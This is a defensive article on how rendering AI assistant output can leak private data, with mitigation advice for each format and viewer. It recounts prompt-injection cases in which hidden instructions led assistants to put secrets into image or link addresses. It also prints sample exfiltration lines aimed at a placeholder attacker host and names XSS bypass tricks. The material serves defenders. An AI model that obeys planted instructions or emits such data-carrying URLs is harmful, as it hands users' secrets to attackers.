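# Preventing data leaks when AI output is displayed: image blocking, allowlists, URL checks and output scanning

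## How displaying an answer can send data to a stranger

The large language model behind an AI assistant produces plain text, which the chat window, mail client or document editor then renders, or turns into a formatted page with headings, tables, links and pictures. Most assistants write in Markdown, a shorthand in which a pattern of brackets stands for a picture. The picture itself is usually stored on another server, and the app has to request it by its web address, or URL. The model writes that URL as part of its answer. If a third party has influenced what the model writes, the URL can contain the user's private data, and displaying the answer then sends that data to whoever runs the server. Security researchers call this exfiltration, which means moving private data to someone who is not entitled to it.

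The leak requires neither a virus on the user's computer nor a break-in at the assistant's maker. The browser fetches pictures, as browsers have done since the 1990s. The unusual part is that the program writing the page also reads mail from strangers and may act on what it reads.

### Prompt injection

An assistant that summarises a document receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and the document as one long text. In prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by hiding instructions in content the model will read, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. The attacker doesn't need access to the assistant, only a way to get text to it, such as an email, a comment on a web page or a shared file.

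The name "prompt injection" comes from SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a website form and the database runs them. Programmers can prevent this by making the database treat whatever arrives from the form as data, never as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), a post from Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models have no equivalent fix. A model predicts the next piece of text from all the text so far, and nothing inside it separates instructions from data. Developers can make attacks harder by training models to give more weight to the real instructions or by labeling the untrusted parts, but David C thinks prompt injection may never be eliminated the way SQL injection can be.

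Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, credits the discovery of prompt injection to the company Preamble, which reported it to OpenAI in May 2022. The programmer Simon Willison named it later that year. People often confuse it with jailbreaking, in which a user gets a model to say something its maker forbids, but in prompt injection the user is the victim.

### A worked example

Suppose that Dana, who works for a building firm, asks an assistant with access to her mailbox to summarise the morning's mail. One message comes from a stranger. Below its visible text, in white type on a white background, the sender has put instructions meant for an AI assistant. They ask it to look up the price in the firm's latest tender and to end its summary with a picture whose address includes that price. The assistant finds the tender in another email, writes a perfectly good summary, and adds a line of Markdown:

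```
![logo](https://img.attacker.example/logo.png?v=482000)
```

(Internet standards reserve the ending ".example" for illustrations, so the address leads nowhere.) Dana never sees this line. Her chat window converts it into HTML, the language of web pages, before showing it:

```
<img src="https://img.attacker.example/logo.png?v=482000" alt="logo">
```

On meeting an image tag, the browser contacts the named server and asks for the file. The server, like nearly every web server, writes each request into a log:

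```
[05/Dec/2026:09:14:22] "GET /logo.png?v=482000" 200
```

The attacker now has the price, because it was sent in the request. It does not matter whether the server sends back a real logo, a single transparent pixel or an error. Encryption does not help, because it protects the request from eavesdroppers and the attacker is the intended recipient. The leak also works when the assistant has no tool for reaching the internet, because Dana's own browser made the connection.

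Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog, documents the same sequence in a real product, Microsoft's Bing Chat. The hostile text was in a web page the user had open. Rehberger delayed the image for two more turns of conversation so that nothing odd happened at the moment of infection. His server received an encoded summary of the page and the chat, along with a secret from elsewhere on the page. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* reproduces a real log line from September 2023. It has the same parts as Dana's, except that the leaked value is itself a web address, a share link to content on another service.

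Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* describes a May 2026 attack on Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that could email its own user without asking. Those emails could contain remote images, and OneDrive, Microsoft's file store, can issue download links that need no further login. An image address containing one of these links could therefore give an attacker the whole file.

### Where the data fits in a URL

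A URL specifies which server the browser should contact and what to request. In Dana's case, "https" is the connection method and "img.attacker.example" is the host name, which identifies the server. The path, "/logo.png", looks like the location of a file. Everything after the question mark is the query, which can hold extra values such as search terms. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that visiting a website always sends the requested URL to the site, and that sites commonly log it.

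Most published demonstrations put the stolen value in the query, but stripping queries from image addresses would not be enough to prevent leaks, because the path and host name can also carry data. Whoever runs a server decides what its paths mean, so "/482000.png" carries the price as well as "?v=482000" does. A September 2025 attack on the note-taking product Notion, which Willison also recounts, put client names and revenue figures into the path, though the request came from the agent's search tool and not from a picture. The owner of attacker.example can also accept requests for any host name that ends that way, including "482000.attacker.example". Before connecting, the browser must look the name up in the domain name system, the internet's directory. That lookup normally ends at a name server the owner chooses, so the value can get out even if the browser never loads a picture. Willison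 (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, expected attackers to turn to subdomains and file names once vendors began to inspect URLs.

When a browser requests a file, it sends the server every part of the URL except the fragment, which is the part after a "#" sign. Simple encodings let any of the parts it sends carry spaces, accents or whole sentences.

### Three conditions, and the one defenders usually remove

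According to Willison's *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), a system is open to this kind of theft when it has access to private data, takes in content that an attacker could have written, and can communicate with the outside. Dana's assistant meets the first condition because it reads her mailbox and the second because anyone can write to her. It meets the third only because her chat window loads pictures, which is easy to overlook when the developer has given the model no web access. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) gives a similar analysis in two parts. An attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous when misused.

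Removing any one of the three conditions stops the theft, but some are much harder to give up than others. Access to private data is usually the reason for having the assistant. Untrusted content is nearly as hard to give up. NVIDIA's AI red team, which attacks the company's AI systems before release to find their weaknesses, notes that anyone who emails a user can add text to the material the assistant searches. It adds that shutting these senders out often defeats the purpose of the product, and suggests partial measures, such as keeping outside mail as a separate source. By comparison, a mail summary loses little if it cannot show pictures from arbitrary servers.

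Blocking requests in the viewer is also more predictable than relying on the model to refuse a planted instruction, which it will do only with some probability. OpenAI reports that safety training leads ChatGPT to refuse in most of the attacks known to the company. The same article reproduces part of a 2025 email attack that worked in half of OpenAI's tests. Models have become harder to fool since then, but an attacker can reword the message and send it to thousands of people. Willison objects to products that promise to catch 95% of attacks because web security counts 95% as a failure. A viewer that will not contact unknown servers behaves the same way however persuasive the email is, and David C recommends building on fixed safeguards like this, which do not depend on a model's judgement. OpenAI did so in Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that limits outgoing requests and reached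 personal accounts in June 2026. Willison welcomed it, but inferred that ChatGPT without the setting does not robustly withstand a determined attacker.

Blocking the route by which data leaves protects only secrets. The injected instructions remain in the model's input, and OpenAI warns in its description of Lockdown Mode that they can still make an answer wrong. In 2023, Rehberger showed that a hostile document could make the AI features in Google Docs tell the reader to call a scammer, which no rule about remote images would prevent.

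### Zero-click and one-click leaks

Dana's leak is zero-click because it happens as soon as her screen shows the answer. If the assistant had written an ordinary link, the price would have leaked only when she clicked it, making it a one-click leak. A zero-click leak may still require the user to do something other than click. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), published on 3 December, describes three zero-click leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant built into Microsoft's office programs. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), in each leak a hostile email could sit unread until its recipient asked Copilot for something legitimate and Copilot retrieved the email. The data then left through an image URL, a link to a saved file, or code. Microsoft had closed all three routes by 15 November, and the researchers knew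 of no real attacks. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) adds that in the image route, the data reached the attacker's server through Bing, Microsoft's search engine.

One-click leaks also still occur, and Underhill (2026) reported one in June in *SearchLeak Flaw Exposed Sensitive Data in Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Requiring a click protects users less than it might seem to, because a link's visible text need not match its destination. In a case that Rehberger reported to Microsoft in early 2024, a phishing email caused Copilot to fetch material from the user's inbox and write it into a link in invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024. Amazon stopped rendering links in its Amazon Q for Business assistant when it faced a leak through them.

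Slack, Telegram and similar messaging programs fetch the page behind any link that arrives, without waiting for a click, so they can show a preview. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* warns that an agent which talks to its user through such a program can therefore leak data as soon as it sends a link, and found that OpenClaw, a popular open-source assistant, is exposed by default when people use it over Telegram. The same line of text can be harmless in one viewer, leak data after a click in another and leak it without a click in a third. Besides pictures, SVG drawings, LaTeX formulas and diagrams can also cause requests in some viewers.

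The term "data leak" is often also used for a different failure, in which an assistant shows an employee a file, such as a salary record, that the employee has no right to read. NVIDIA's team sees this regularly and traces it to three causes: the original documents had the wrong permissions, the assistant's searchable copy did not preserve the permissions, or a change in permissions reached that copy late. Blocking images does not help here, because nothing is sent to an outsider. Checking each user's permissions before the model sees the document prevents this failure.

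### From the first reports to the present

Roman Samoilenko found the image leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. Willison (2023) explained in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* that Samoilenko's version relied on a web page that altered whatever the visitor copied from it, so that the victim pasted the hostile instructions into ChatGPT by hand. Rehberger independently found the same leak a few days later. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger (2023) showed that the pasting was unnecessary once ChatGPT could read web pages through plugins, add-ons that connected it to other services. The page's author could then take the conversation history directly.

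Rehberger reported the problem to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI on 9 April. OpenAI answered that rendering images was a feature and that it planned no change. Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed Bing Chat. As far as he could tell from outside, the main change was a content security policy (CSP), a set of rules that a website sends to the browser to limit where it may load images and other resources from. The policy named four Bing hosts. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* (2026), Rehberger dates the fix to May. Both dates can be right if the policy took effect before Microsoft wrote to him.

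OpenAI changed course in December 2023. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the first check. Before showing an image, the ChatGPT web page sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, which classified it as safe or unsafe. OpenAI did not publish the criteria. Rehberger's obvious test address failed the check, but when he tried 36 addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, nine passed, enough to spell out short words one request at a time. The check ran only in the web version, and both the iPhone app and the Mac app that OpenAI released in 2024 lacked it. Rehberger used that gap to plant instructions in ChatGPT's long-term memory, which made every later conversation leak too. OpenAI has since rebuilt the check around a record of addresses already public on the web.

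The flaw kept appearing in other products. By the end of 2024, Rehberger alone had reported it in eleven, including Anthropic's Claude, GitHub Copilot Chat and several from Google. Willison observed that vendors usually fixed their own products promptly, most often by blocking the route through which data could leave, but each new product could repeat the mistake. In October 2025, two and a half years after the first reports, NVIDIA's red team still listed the rendering of active content among its three most significant findings. This is good evidence that developers still make the mistake, but the team gave no figures to show how many do.

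NVIDIA recommends that developers use a CSP that allows images only from a fixed list of safe sites. It also recommends showing users the full link before opening it, or making links inactive so that users have to copy and paste them. Developers should also try to strip Markdown, HTML and URLs from the model's output and, as a last resort, disable active content altogether. This order is open to dispute, since disabling active content leaves the least to go wrong.

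Products now use five defenses, often in combination. Some load no remote content, so an answer cannot cause the viewer to contact another server. Others load content only from sites on an allowlist. A stricter approach, which OpenAI currently uses, approves exact addresses based on where they came from, on the reasoning that a URL already public before the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's secrets. Output scanning searches the generated text for sensitive data and suspicious links, and masks or blocks them before delivery. The fifth defense is to show the user the address and let them decide whether to open it.

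## Which output formats and viewers make network requests

All five defenses depend on knowing where a URL can appear in an answer and what the viewer does with it. Each format has its own rules for which elements trigger a network request when displayed and which do so only when clicked.

### Markdown

Dana's assistant wrote an inline image, in which the address stands in round brackets directly after the picture's label. Markdown also has a reference style, which puts the address somewhere else in the answer:

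```
![logo][1]

(the rest of the summary)

[1]: https://img.attacker.example/logo.png?v=482000
```

The browser requests a Markdown image at the same moment whether its address is written inline or in a separate reference. A filter that searches only for the inline pattern misses the reference style, which is how the EchoLeak attack of 2025 got past Microsoft's link filter in Copilot. A filter works better if it runs after the parser, the part of the renderer that sorts text into paragraphs, links and images, because the parser turns both styles into the same kind of object, an image with an address.

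Links also come in inline and reference styles. Renderers turn an address in angle brackets into a link too, and many do the same for a bare address in running text. All of these links make a request only when clicked. Deleting the link syntax isn't enough to make an answer safe if the renderer links bare addresses, because it will turn the remaining address back into a link.

Markdown is designed to allow raw HTML in the text. According to Snyk's *Same href, different syntax* (2026), some renderers disable raw HTML by default, others allow all of it, and many leave sanitizing to the application. If the HTML reaches the viewer intact, a Markdown answer can trigger network requests in every way that HTML can.

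Markstream is a Markdown renderer designed with AI output in mind. Markstream's *Security* recommends its "safe" policy for AI chat. This policy removes scripts, inline styles and dangerous kinds of address, but still loads images from any http or https server. It blocks addresses that begin with two slashes because they can silently load outside resources, although the addresses it permits can do the same. For developers who want no outside requests, *Security* suggests a policy called "escape" that shows all HTML as plain text, a custom image component, a CSP, or an image proxy, which is a server that fetches images on the user's behalf. The "escape" policy looks insufficient alone because, by its description, it covers HTML, while images in Markdown notation have separate rules that allow any web server. A developer would therefore need to replace the image component too.

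An answer can also contain the image itself, encoded in an address that begins with "data:", so the browser doesn't need to fetch it. Markstream allows these addresses for photographs and other bitmap images but not for SVG drawings.

### HTML and style sheets

HTML has many more ways to trigger a network request than Markdown does. Images alone have several, including the image tag's main address, its list of alternative sizes, a video's preview frame and an old attribute for page backgrounds. Frames load an entire page from elsewhere. A redirect tag can send the user's browser to another site after a set delay, without a click.

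Style sheets, written in CSS, control a page's appearance and can name addresses for background pictures, fonts and further style sheets. The browser fetches a background when something on the page uses a rule that names it, and a font when some text needs it. A single style attribute on an otherwise harmless paragraph is enough to cause a request. CSS can also leak data that the model never wrote into an address. A rule may apply only when an element on the page has a certain value, and each rule can name a different picture. Whoever runs the server can then tell what the page contained by seeing which picture the browser requests.

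Prefetch tags tell the browser to fetch a page before the user opens it. Some variants only look up a host name or open a connection, so no file request appears in a log. But the lookup alone can leak the price, as Dana's example showed.

A form sends its contents when the user presses a button. It can send them in the body of the request, where a check that examines only URLs won't find them, and it can include hidden fields that the model has already filled in. Links, image maps (pictures with clickable regions) and links inside drawings and formulas also need a click. All of these appear in a demonstration page for DOMPurify, an open-source sanitiser that many websites run over HTML from outsiders. Another of the project's test pages lists ways to trigger automatic requests, starting with places few developers would think to check, such as the document-type line at the top of a page and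 an attribute that once listed files for offline use. Current browsers ignore some of these, but the length of the list is still a good argument against removing triggers one by one.

For most chat windows, the safe setting is to show HTML as text. A product that needs some formatting can allow a short list of tags that don't take a URL, such as table and bold tags, and remove all style attributes. Products that let the model build whole web pages usually display them in a sandboxed frame that has its own restrictions.

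### Why a sanitiser can pass a leak

Developers often rely on a sanitiser to make a model's output safe. Sanitisers protect against the threat they were built for, cross-site scripting (XSS), in which an attacker gets code to run inside someone else's web page, where it can read the page and act as the user. They generally allow images from other sites, because the images run no code and web pages have always included them, so removing them would break ordinary content.

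DOMPurify's documented default is to guard against XSS and a related attack while permitting links to any resource that doesn't cause XSS. Developers who want to control requests have to add a hook, which is their own code that runs during cleaning. The project supplies an example that rewrites every known outside address to go through a proxy. The example covers six HTML attributes, inline styles and the CSS rules for fonts and animations. It also deletes imported style sheets and forbids SVG. DOMPurify's maintainers call it a "monster" in their documentation. Even with this rewriting, a proxy that forwards the full address to the attacker's server still delivers the data. Google took a simpler approach with Gemini's sanitiser, which blocks external images.

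Ordinary security advice can be sound against scripts and still let image requests through. To stop malicious links, Snyk recommends accepting only protocols such as http and https, passing the result through DOMPurify, and using a CSP that blocks inline scripts. Dana's picture would pass every check because it has an https address, it contains no code, and the CSP rule governs scripts, not images.

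Any filter that compares image addresses with a list needs to decode them first, or it will check a different address from the one the browser contacts. Script filtering in Goldmark, a popular Markdown renderer, had this flaw. Goldmark compared each address with a list of dangerous beginnings before decoding the codes that HTML uses for punctuation. An attacker could write the colon in "javascript:" as such a code and pass the check, and Goldmark would then restore the colon. Hugo, a program for building websites, inherited the flaw. Goldmark's developers fixed it by decoding addresses before checking them.

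### SVG drawings

SVG is a text format for drawings that uses tags for lines, shapes and labels, so a language model can write a chart or an icon directly. The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which maintains the standard, describes in *Chapter 12* two ways a drawing can include other content. The "image" element imports a picture, and the "foreignObject" element holds fragments of other languages, including HTML.

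What the browser does with such content depends on how the page includes the drawing. W3C's *SVG Integration* (2025), a working draft, lays down the rules:

- If the application pastes the SVG tags into its own page, the drawing has the same freedom as the page. Scripts can run and outside references load.
- A drawing in a frame, or in HTML's "object" or "embed" element, also gets both.
- If the page shows the drawing through an ordinary image tag, the browser runs no scripts and treats every outside reference as a failed download.

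Browsers adopted the restriction on images long before this draft. Mozilla added it to Firefox in 2011 in response to the bug report *SVG-as-an-image shouldn't be able to load external resources*. Its developers blocked even resources on the page's own site, because a redirect there could send the request to another site. On a W3C mailing list, the standards editor Anne van Kesteren described the worry as people hiding tracking images in the SVGs they upload. The restriction has failed at least once. Mozilla's *SVG-as-an-image sends requests for external files* describes a 2016 flaw that let external requests through using "data:" addresses. Mozilla rated the flaw high severity and then fixed it.

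An application can display an SVG drawing that a model wrote by encoding it as a "data:" address and putting that address in an image tag. Willison (2024), in *Mastodon discussion about sandboxing SVG data*, preferred this to searching for harmful tags. In a test with a drawing that contained a script, the image tag showed the drawing and ignored the script, but opening the same picture in a new tab ran the script. According to the documentation of Grida, a design tool, this method also protects against tricks that a sanitiser would miss, because the browser doesn't have to recognise them. However, users can't select text in the drawing or click on its parts, and outside fonts fail without a warning. The address also has to be a "data:" address because an image tag that points to a drawing on the attacker's server still requests it, even if the browser then makes its contents harmless.

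INCIBE's *CVE-2025-43714* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, records that until at least 30 March 2025 ChatGPT drew SVG code inside its own page instead of displaying it as text, which let an attacker inject HTML. (A CVE number identifies a flaw in a public catalogue.) Cyber Security News adds that this happened when someone reopened a chat or followed a public link to one, and warns of phishing. It also describes the flaw as effectively a form of cross-site scripting (XSS), a stronger claim than the catalogue entry makes. Neither account shows private data leaking through an SVG.

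### LaTeX formulas and documents

Models write formulas in LaTeX, the notation scientists use to type mathematics. Most chat windows convert these formulas to HTML in the browser with the KaTeX or MathJax library. Both libraries accept some commands that have little to do with mathematics.

In KaTeX, a setting called "trust" controls them. KaTeX's *Options* gives its default value as false, in which case the library prints a suspicious command in the color it uses for errors and does not carry it out. The commands behave differently once a developer turns trust on:

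- `\includegraphics` inserts a picture from an address, which the browser requests as soon as it shows the formula.
- `\href` and `\url` make links, which wait for a click.
- `\htmlStyle` adds a CSS style to part of the formula. Since CSS can name outside pictures, this could presumably cause an automatic request too.
- `\htmlClass`, `\htmlId` and `\htmlData` attach other HTML attributes.

KaTeX's *Security* warns that the `trust` setting permits commands that may load external resources. Developers can set `trust` to a function that decides case by case, using the command, the address and the protocol (such as "https"). Several sample functions in the documentation approve any command whose address uses an accepted protocol. This blocks scripts, but `\includegraphics` can still load an image from any https server and leak data. To prevent leaks, the function has to refuse `\includegraphics`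 or check the host.

Developers turn trust on for good reasons. The forum software Discourse allowed `\href` so that readers could jump from a mention of an equation to the equation itself. Its trust function approved the command without checking the link's protocol. Snyk found that this let any logged-in user post a formula that ran JavaScript when someone clicked it.

Two flaws in KaTeX show that even a carefully written trust function may fail. Tenable's *CVE-2024-28246* (2024) concerns functions that refuse the protocol "javascript". KaTeX passed on the protocol exactly as the formula's author typed it, so capital letters got past the check, and browsers ignore case. A function that listed the protocols to accept would have rejected the odd spelling. Version 0.16.10 fixed the flaw. The second flaw, from January 2025, depended less on how the developer wrote the function. NVD's *CVE-2025-23207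 Detail*, in the US government's vulnerability database, reports that a formula with `\htmlData` could run any JavaScript when an application rendered it with a common KaTeX function. A script does more harm than a single image request because it can read the whole page and send any of it elsewhere. Developers who couldn't move to version 0.16.21 could forbid the command or turn trust off, which also prevents the first flaw from being exploited.

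MathJax has a filter called ui/safe, which a site must load explicitly. MathJax's *Safe Extension Options* shows that by default the filter blocks "javascript:" and "data:" addresses but allows http, https and file addresses, so a link to an attacker's server goes through unchanged. Developers can set the filter's URL option to "none", which removes every address from the formula.

That stricter setting also avoids a flaw in the filter. Snyk found that a line break inside the word "javascript" kept the filter from detecting a protocol, and the filter allowed addresses without one. MathJax's developers fixed this in version 4 but not in version 3, and versions 2 and 3 still have far more users than version 4. Version 4 also added the ability to display HTML inside a formula, and MathJax's *Support for HTML in MathML and TeX* warns that the library does not sanitise this HTML. The feature is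 off unless a site loads and enables it, and a site that shows AI output has little reason to do either.

Some products compile a complete LaTeX document on a server to produce a PDF. LaTeX has a command that reads in another file, which authors use to split long books into chapters. Unless someone restricts it, the compiler can often read any file that its account can open. An optional mode also lets documents run system commands. A planted instruction could therefore put the contents of a configuration file into the PDF. An attacker gets those contents only if they obtain the PDF, if the reader clicks a link that contains the contents, or if the compiler can connect to the internet. Operators can run the compiler in an isolated container with no network connection, no secrets on its disk, and system commands turned off.

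There seems to be no public report of an AI product leaking a user's data through a LaTeX formula, a compiled LaTeX document or a plain SVG drawing. These risks are inferred from what the formats can do. But researchers have extracted real data through diagrams.

### Mermaid diagrams

Mermaid is a small language for diagrams. A line such as "User --> Computer" becomes two boxes and an arrow, and the diagram is normally an SVG drawing. The text in a box can contain HTML, including image tags.

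Cursor, a code editor with a built-in AI agent, displayed Mermaid diagrams in its chat. In Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE*, Rehberger reports that when he asked for a diagram containing a remote picture, Cursor requested the picture without any confirmation. He then hid instructions in a comment in a source file and asked Cursor to explain the file. In one demonstration, the agent searched the project for API keys and put one from a configuration file into the picture's address. In another, it sent the notes Cursor had saved about the developer. The diagram appears all at once, so the user can't spot a long, suspicious address as it is being written. Rehberger reported the flaw, CVE-2025-54132, on 30 June 2025. Cursor resolved it a week later, and the fix was available in version 1.3 from 29 July.

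Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *Takedown*, found the same kind of flaw by examining how eight coding agents handled the special notations in a model's output. In one agent, which they anonymized as A2, the Mermaid renderer loaded external images without asking the user. In their full attack, hidden instructions in a public bug report led the agent to read a settings file elsewhere on the developer's computer without permission, and a diagram carried an API key from that file to the attacker's server. The vendor already knew of the leak when they reported it.

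A2 had no built-in tool for fetching web pages, and by default it asked the user before running terminal commands. A reviewer checking the agent's tools for internet access could have overlooked the diagram, since drawing one does not count as a tool. Lee and colleagues took files from anywhere on the computer in four of the eight agents, but not always through a diagram. In another agent, they used the web-fetching tool, which required no approval.

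Markstream cleans the finished Mermaid diagram whether or not the developer has chosen Mermaid's strict mode. It removes "foreignObject", the element that holds HTML labels, and leaves click actions off. A product could also show the finished diagram through an image tag. The browser would then block the diagram's outside references, but its boxes would not be clickable.

### Link previews

Link previews in Slack, Discord and Telegram let a link leak data without the user clicking it. The service's server usually requests the linked page, so a CSP or an image filter in the user's browser can't block the request.

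The remedy is to turn off link previews on the sending side. For Slack, Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, passes on Rehberger's advice to set `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false with each message. For OpenClaw over Telegram, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* recommends adding `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram part of the configuration file. These settings stop the data from leaving when the message arrives, but clicking the link would still send it.

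PromptArmor also runs a test site that records which services fetch a preview and what data the request contained, so that users can check their own combination of agent and messaging program. The result depends on both, because the messaging company has to offer a way to turn previews off and the agent's developer has to use it. PromptArmor would like the services to let people turn previews off for a single chat or channel, so that they can keep the feature elsewhere.

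### Messages an agent sends to its own user

The May 2026 attack on Copilot Cowork relied on an exception to the agent's approval rule. According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams, the company's chat program. But according to PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, Cowork sends messages to the user without asking, and users have no setting to change this. Teams and Outlook load the images in a message when its recipient opens it. The exception probably looked harmless because a message to oneself reveals nothing to anyone else.

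PromptArmor's demonstration started with a skill, a file of instructions for doing a task that users often download from the internet. Five of the file's 81 lines were malicious. The user asked for a review of the week's work, which triggered the skill. The agent, Cowork, collected links that let anyone download recent files without logging in, put them into image URLs, and posted the images in a Teams message to the user. Opening Teams sent the links to the attacker. Cowork's action log showed that it had posted a message but not what the message contained, so a user who checked the log would have found nothing odd.

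The attack succeeded in all five trials, which is too few to estimate a success rate but enough to show that the route worked from end to end. With Claude Opus 4.7, then among the most capable models available, the agent searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents than with automatic model selection. Users can also schedule a weekly review to run unattended, in which case the attack would repeat each time.

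Administrators can limit the damage by blocking downloads from SharePoint, where companies keep shared files, but people then can't print or sync those files or open them in Word and Excel. It would be much less disruptive if Teams and Outlook didn't load remote pictures in messages that an agent wrote, or if Cowork removed the pictures before sending.

### Logs, previews and other forgotten viewers

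A developer can fully secure the chat window and still leak the user's data from somewhere else. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows this with a mock application that banks would use to verify customers' identities. The application combined customers' passport and financial details with material from web sources, one of which contained hidden instructions. Following them, the model wrote an image whose URL contained the customer's data. A second model, which inspected each answer, flagged this one, and the application never displayed it.

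The defense worked, but it also marked the conversation for review, and a developer reviewing it would likely open it in OpenAI's log viewer. The viewer rendered the stored answer as Markdown, including images, and the developer's browser sent the customer's details to the attacker. The application's CSP did not apply because the log viewer is a different website. Displaying answers as plain text or removing images in the application would not have helped either, because the log kept the model's original output. In an example from PromptArmor, a Perplexity answer looked oddly empty after the product removed an image from it. A puzzled user might press the thumbs-down button, which would send the answer to a reviewer.

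PromptArmor found the same behavior in the preview screens where developers test chats, assistants and agents before release, and in a starter application that OpenAI gives developers to build on. The starter application may matter most in the long run, because products that begin as copies of it use the same renderer. PromptArmor reported the log viewer flaw on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, which screens reports for OpenAI, and Bugcrowd closed the case on 4 December as not applicable. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, and on 22 January 2026 it said a fix was under way.

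ChatGPT's iPhone and Mac apps had the same weakness when they lacked the web version's image check. Copies of a model's answer may also appear later in exported chats, email notifications, support tickets or a company's monitoring dashboard. A team could clean the text before storing it, which protects all of these at once but destroys evidence that an investigator needs. The team could instead keep the original and have every internal tool display it as plain text. This preserves the evidence, but the risk returns if someone later adds a tool that renders Markdown.

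| Format or viewer | What triggers a request | Safe setting |
|---|---|---|
| Markdown image, inline or reference style | Displaying the answer | Remove remote images after parsing |
| Markdown link, including automatic links | A click, or a preview by the viewer | Show the address as inactive text |
| HTML and CSS | Displaying images, frames, styles, fonts or prefetch tags; clicking links or submitting forms | Show HTML as text, or permit only tags that take no address |
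| SVG inside the page or in a frame | Displaying the drawing | Put it in an image tag as a "data:" address |
| KaTeX | Displaying `\includegraphics`; clicking `\href` or `\url` | Leave `trust` at false |
| MathJax | Clicking a link in a formula | Load ui/safe with URLs set to "none"; leave HTML in formulas off |
| LaTeX compiler on a server | Compiling the document, if the compiler has network access | Isolated container with no network, no secrets and no system commands |
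| Mermaid diagram | Displaying a diagram with a picture in it | Strip HTML labels and outside pictures, or show the diagram through an image tag |
| Slack message | Arrival of a message with a link | Set `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false |
| OpenClaw over Telegram | Arrival of a message with a link | Set `linkPreview` to false |
| Email or Teams message from an agent | Opening the message | Remove remote images before sending |
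| Developer logs and preview screens | Opening the stored answer | Display as plain text |

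## Loading nothing remote

The strictest of the five defenses is to display every answer without contacting any outside server. If the browser never requests an address, it can't send Dana's price, wherever in the address the model put it. The other defenses depend on someone judging correctly that a site is trustworthy, a scanner recognising a secret, or a busy user reading an address properly, and an attacker can look for a case where that judgement fails. A viewer that loads no remote images gives the attacker no such judgement to exploit, provided its code catches every image.

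Developers can also test this rule easily by displaying many hostile answers, watching the browser's network log, and treating any request to an outside server as a bug. With an allowlist, the log contains many permitted requests, and somebody has to check whether any of them carried data.

Microsoft (2025) calls this kind of rule deterministic because it guarantees that a particular attack will fail, even if the system includes a language model. Microsoft prefers such defenses but says that detecting prompt injection deterministically is still an open research problem. The guarantee covers only that attack, so a rule about images isn't guaranteed to stop attacks that use links or tools.

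Rehberger came to favor the rule after exploiting several products that lacked it. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* describes a data leak through images that he found in 2023 in Generative AI Studio, where developers try out Google's models. As far as he could tell, Google fixed it by no longer turning images or links into HTML, which he called probably the best possible fix for security. Two years later, he described the same kind of leak in a coding agent in Embrace The Red's *Google Jules*. He recommended a CSP and suggested that developers also consider showing no images in chat.

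### From Markdown to a safe page

A strict implementation does its work on the server, in this order, before the display receives anything:

1. Parse the Markdown into a tree of paragraphs, images, links and other nodes.
2. Delete every image node with a remote address, leaving a placeholder. Keep an image only if the answer contains the image data or the application stores the file itself.
3. Escape raw HTML, which means replacing characters such as "<" with codes so that the browser shows the tag as text.
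4. Make links inert by printing the label and the address as plain text.
5. Write new HTML from the cleaned tree and send it to the display.

In pseudocode, the cleaning looks like this:

```
function clean(node):
    if node is text or code:
        return escape(node.text)
    if node is an image:
        if its address is embedded PNG, JPEG, GIF or WebP data:
            return an image tag containing that data
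        if its address is the ID of a file stored for this user:
            return an image tag with the application's address for it
        return "[Image removed: " + escape(node.label) + "]"
    if node is a link:
        return clean(node.label) + " (" + escape(node.address) + ")"
    if node is a paragraph, heading, list, table, bold or italic:
        return a fixed tag around the cleaned contents
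    return escape(node.source)
```

The last line shows raw HTML and anything the developer didn't think of, such as a formula, as source text. New Markdown features therefore look ugly until someone adds support for them, but they don't leak data.

The model refers to a stored file by an ID, and the application looks up the ID and builds the address. If the model could write the address itself, it could add the price to the query, and a redirect on the application's own site might pass the price on to someone else.

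Cleaning the answer on the server avoids a problem in the browser, which can start downloading an image as soon as a script sets an image element's address, even if the element isn't on the page yet. Browser code that builds the answer off the page and then cleans it may therefore be too late. Server code also cleans the answer once for every app, which avoids gaps like the one in ChatGPT's phone app.

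web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* warns that when a sanitiser returns its result as a string, the browser has to parse that string again, and the second result can differ from the one the sanitiser checked. Attackers can exploit the difference. A server that sends HTML can't avoid the second parsing, but the results are unlikely to differ if it writes only a few fixed tags and escapes everything that came from the model. It can also send the cleaned tree as data instead of HTML and let the page build the elements directly.

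### Cleaning a streamed answer

Most assistants stream their answers, so the user sees the beginning while the model is still writing the rest. If the application removes images only after the answer is complete, the browser has already requested them, and any data in their URLs is in the attacker's log. Varonis reported this flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot in *SearchLeak* (2026) and advises developers to sanitise output at the moment of rendering.

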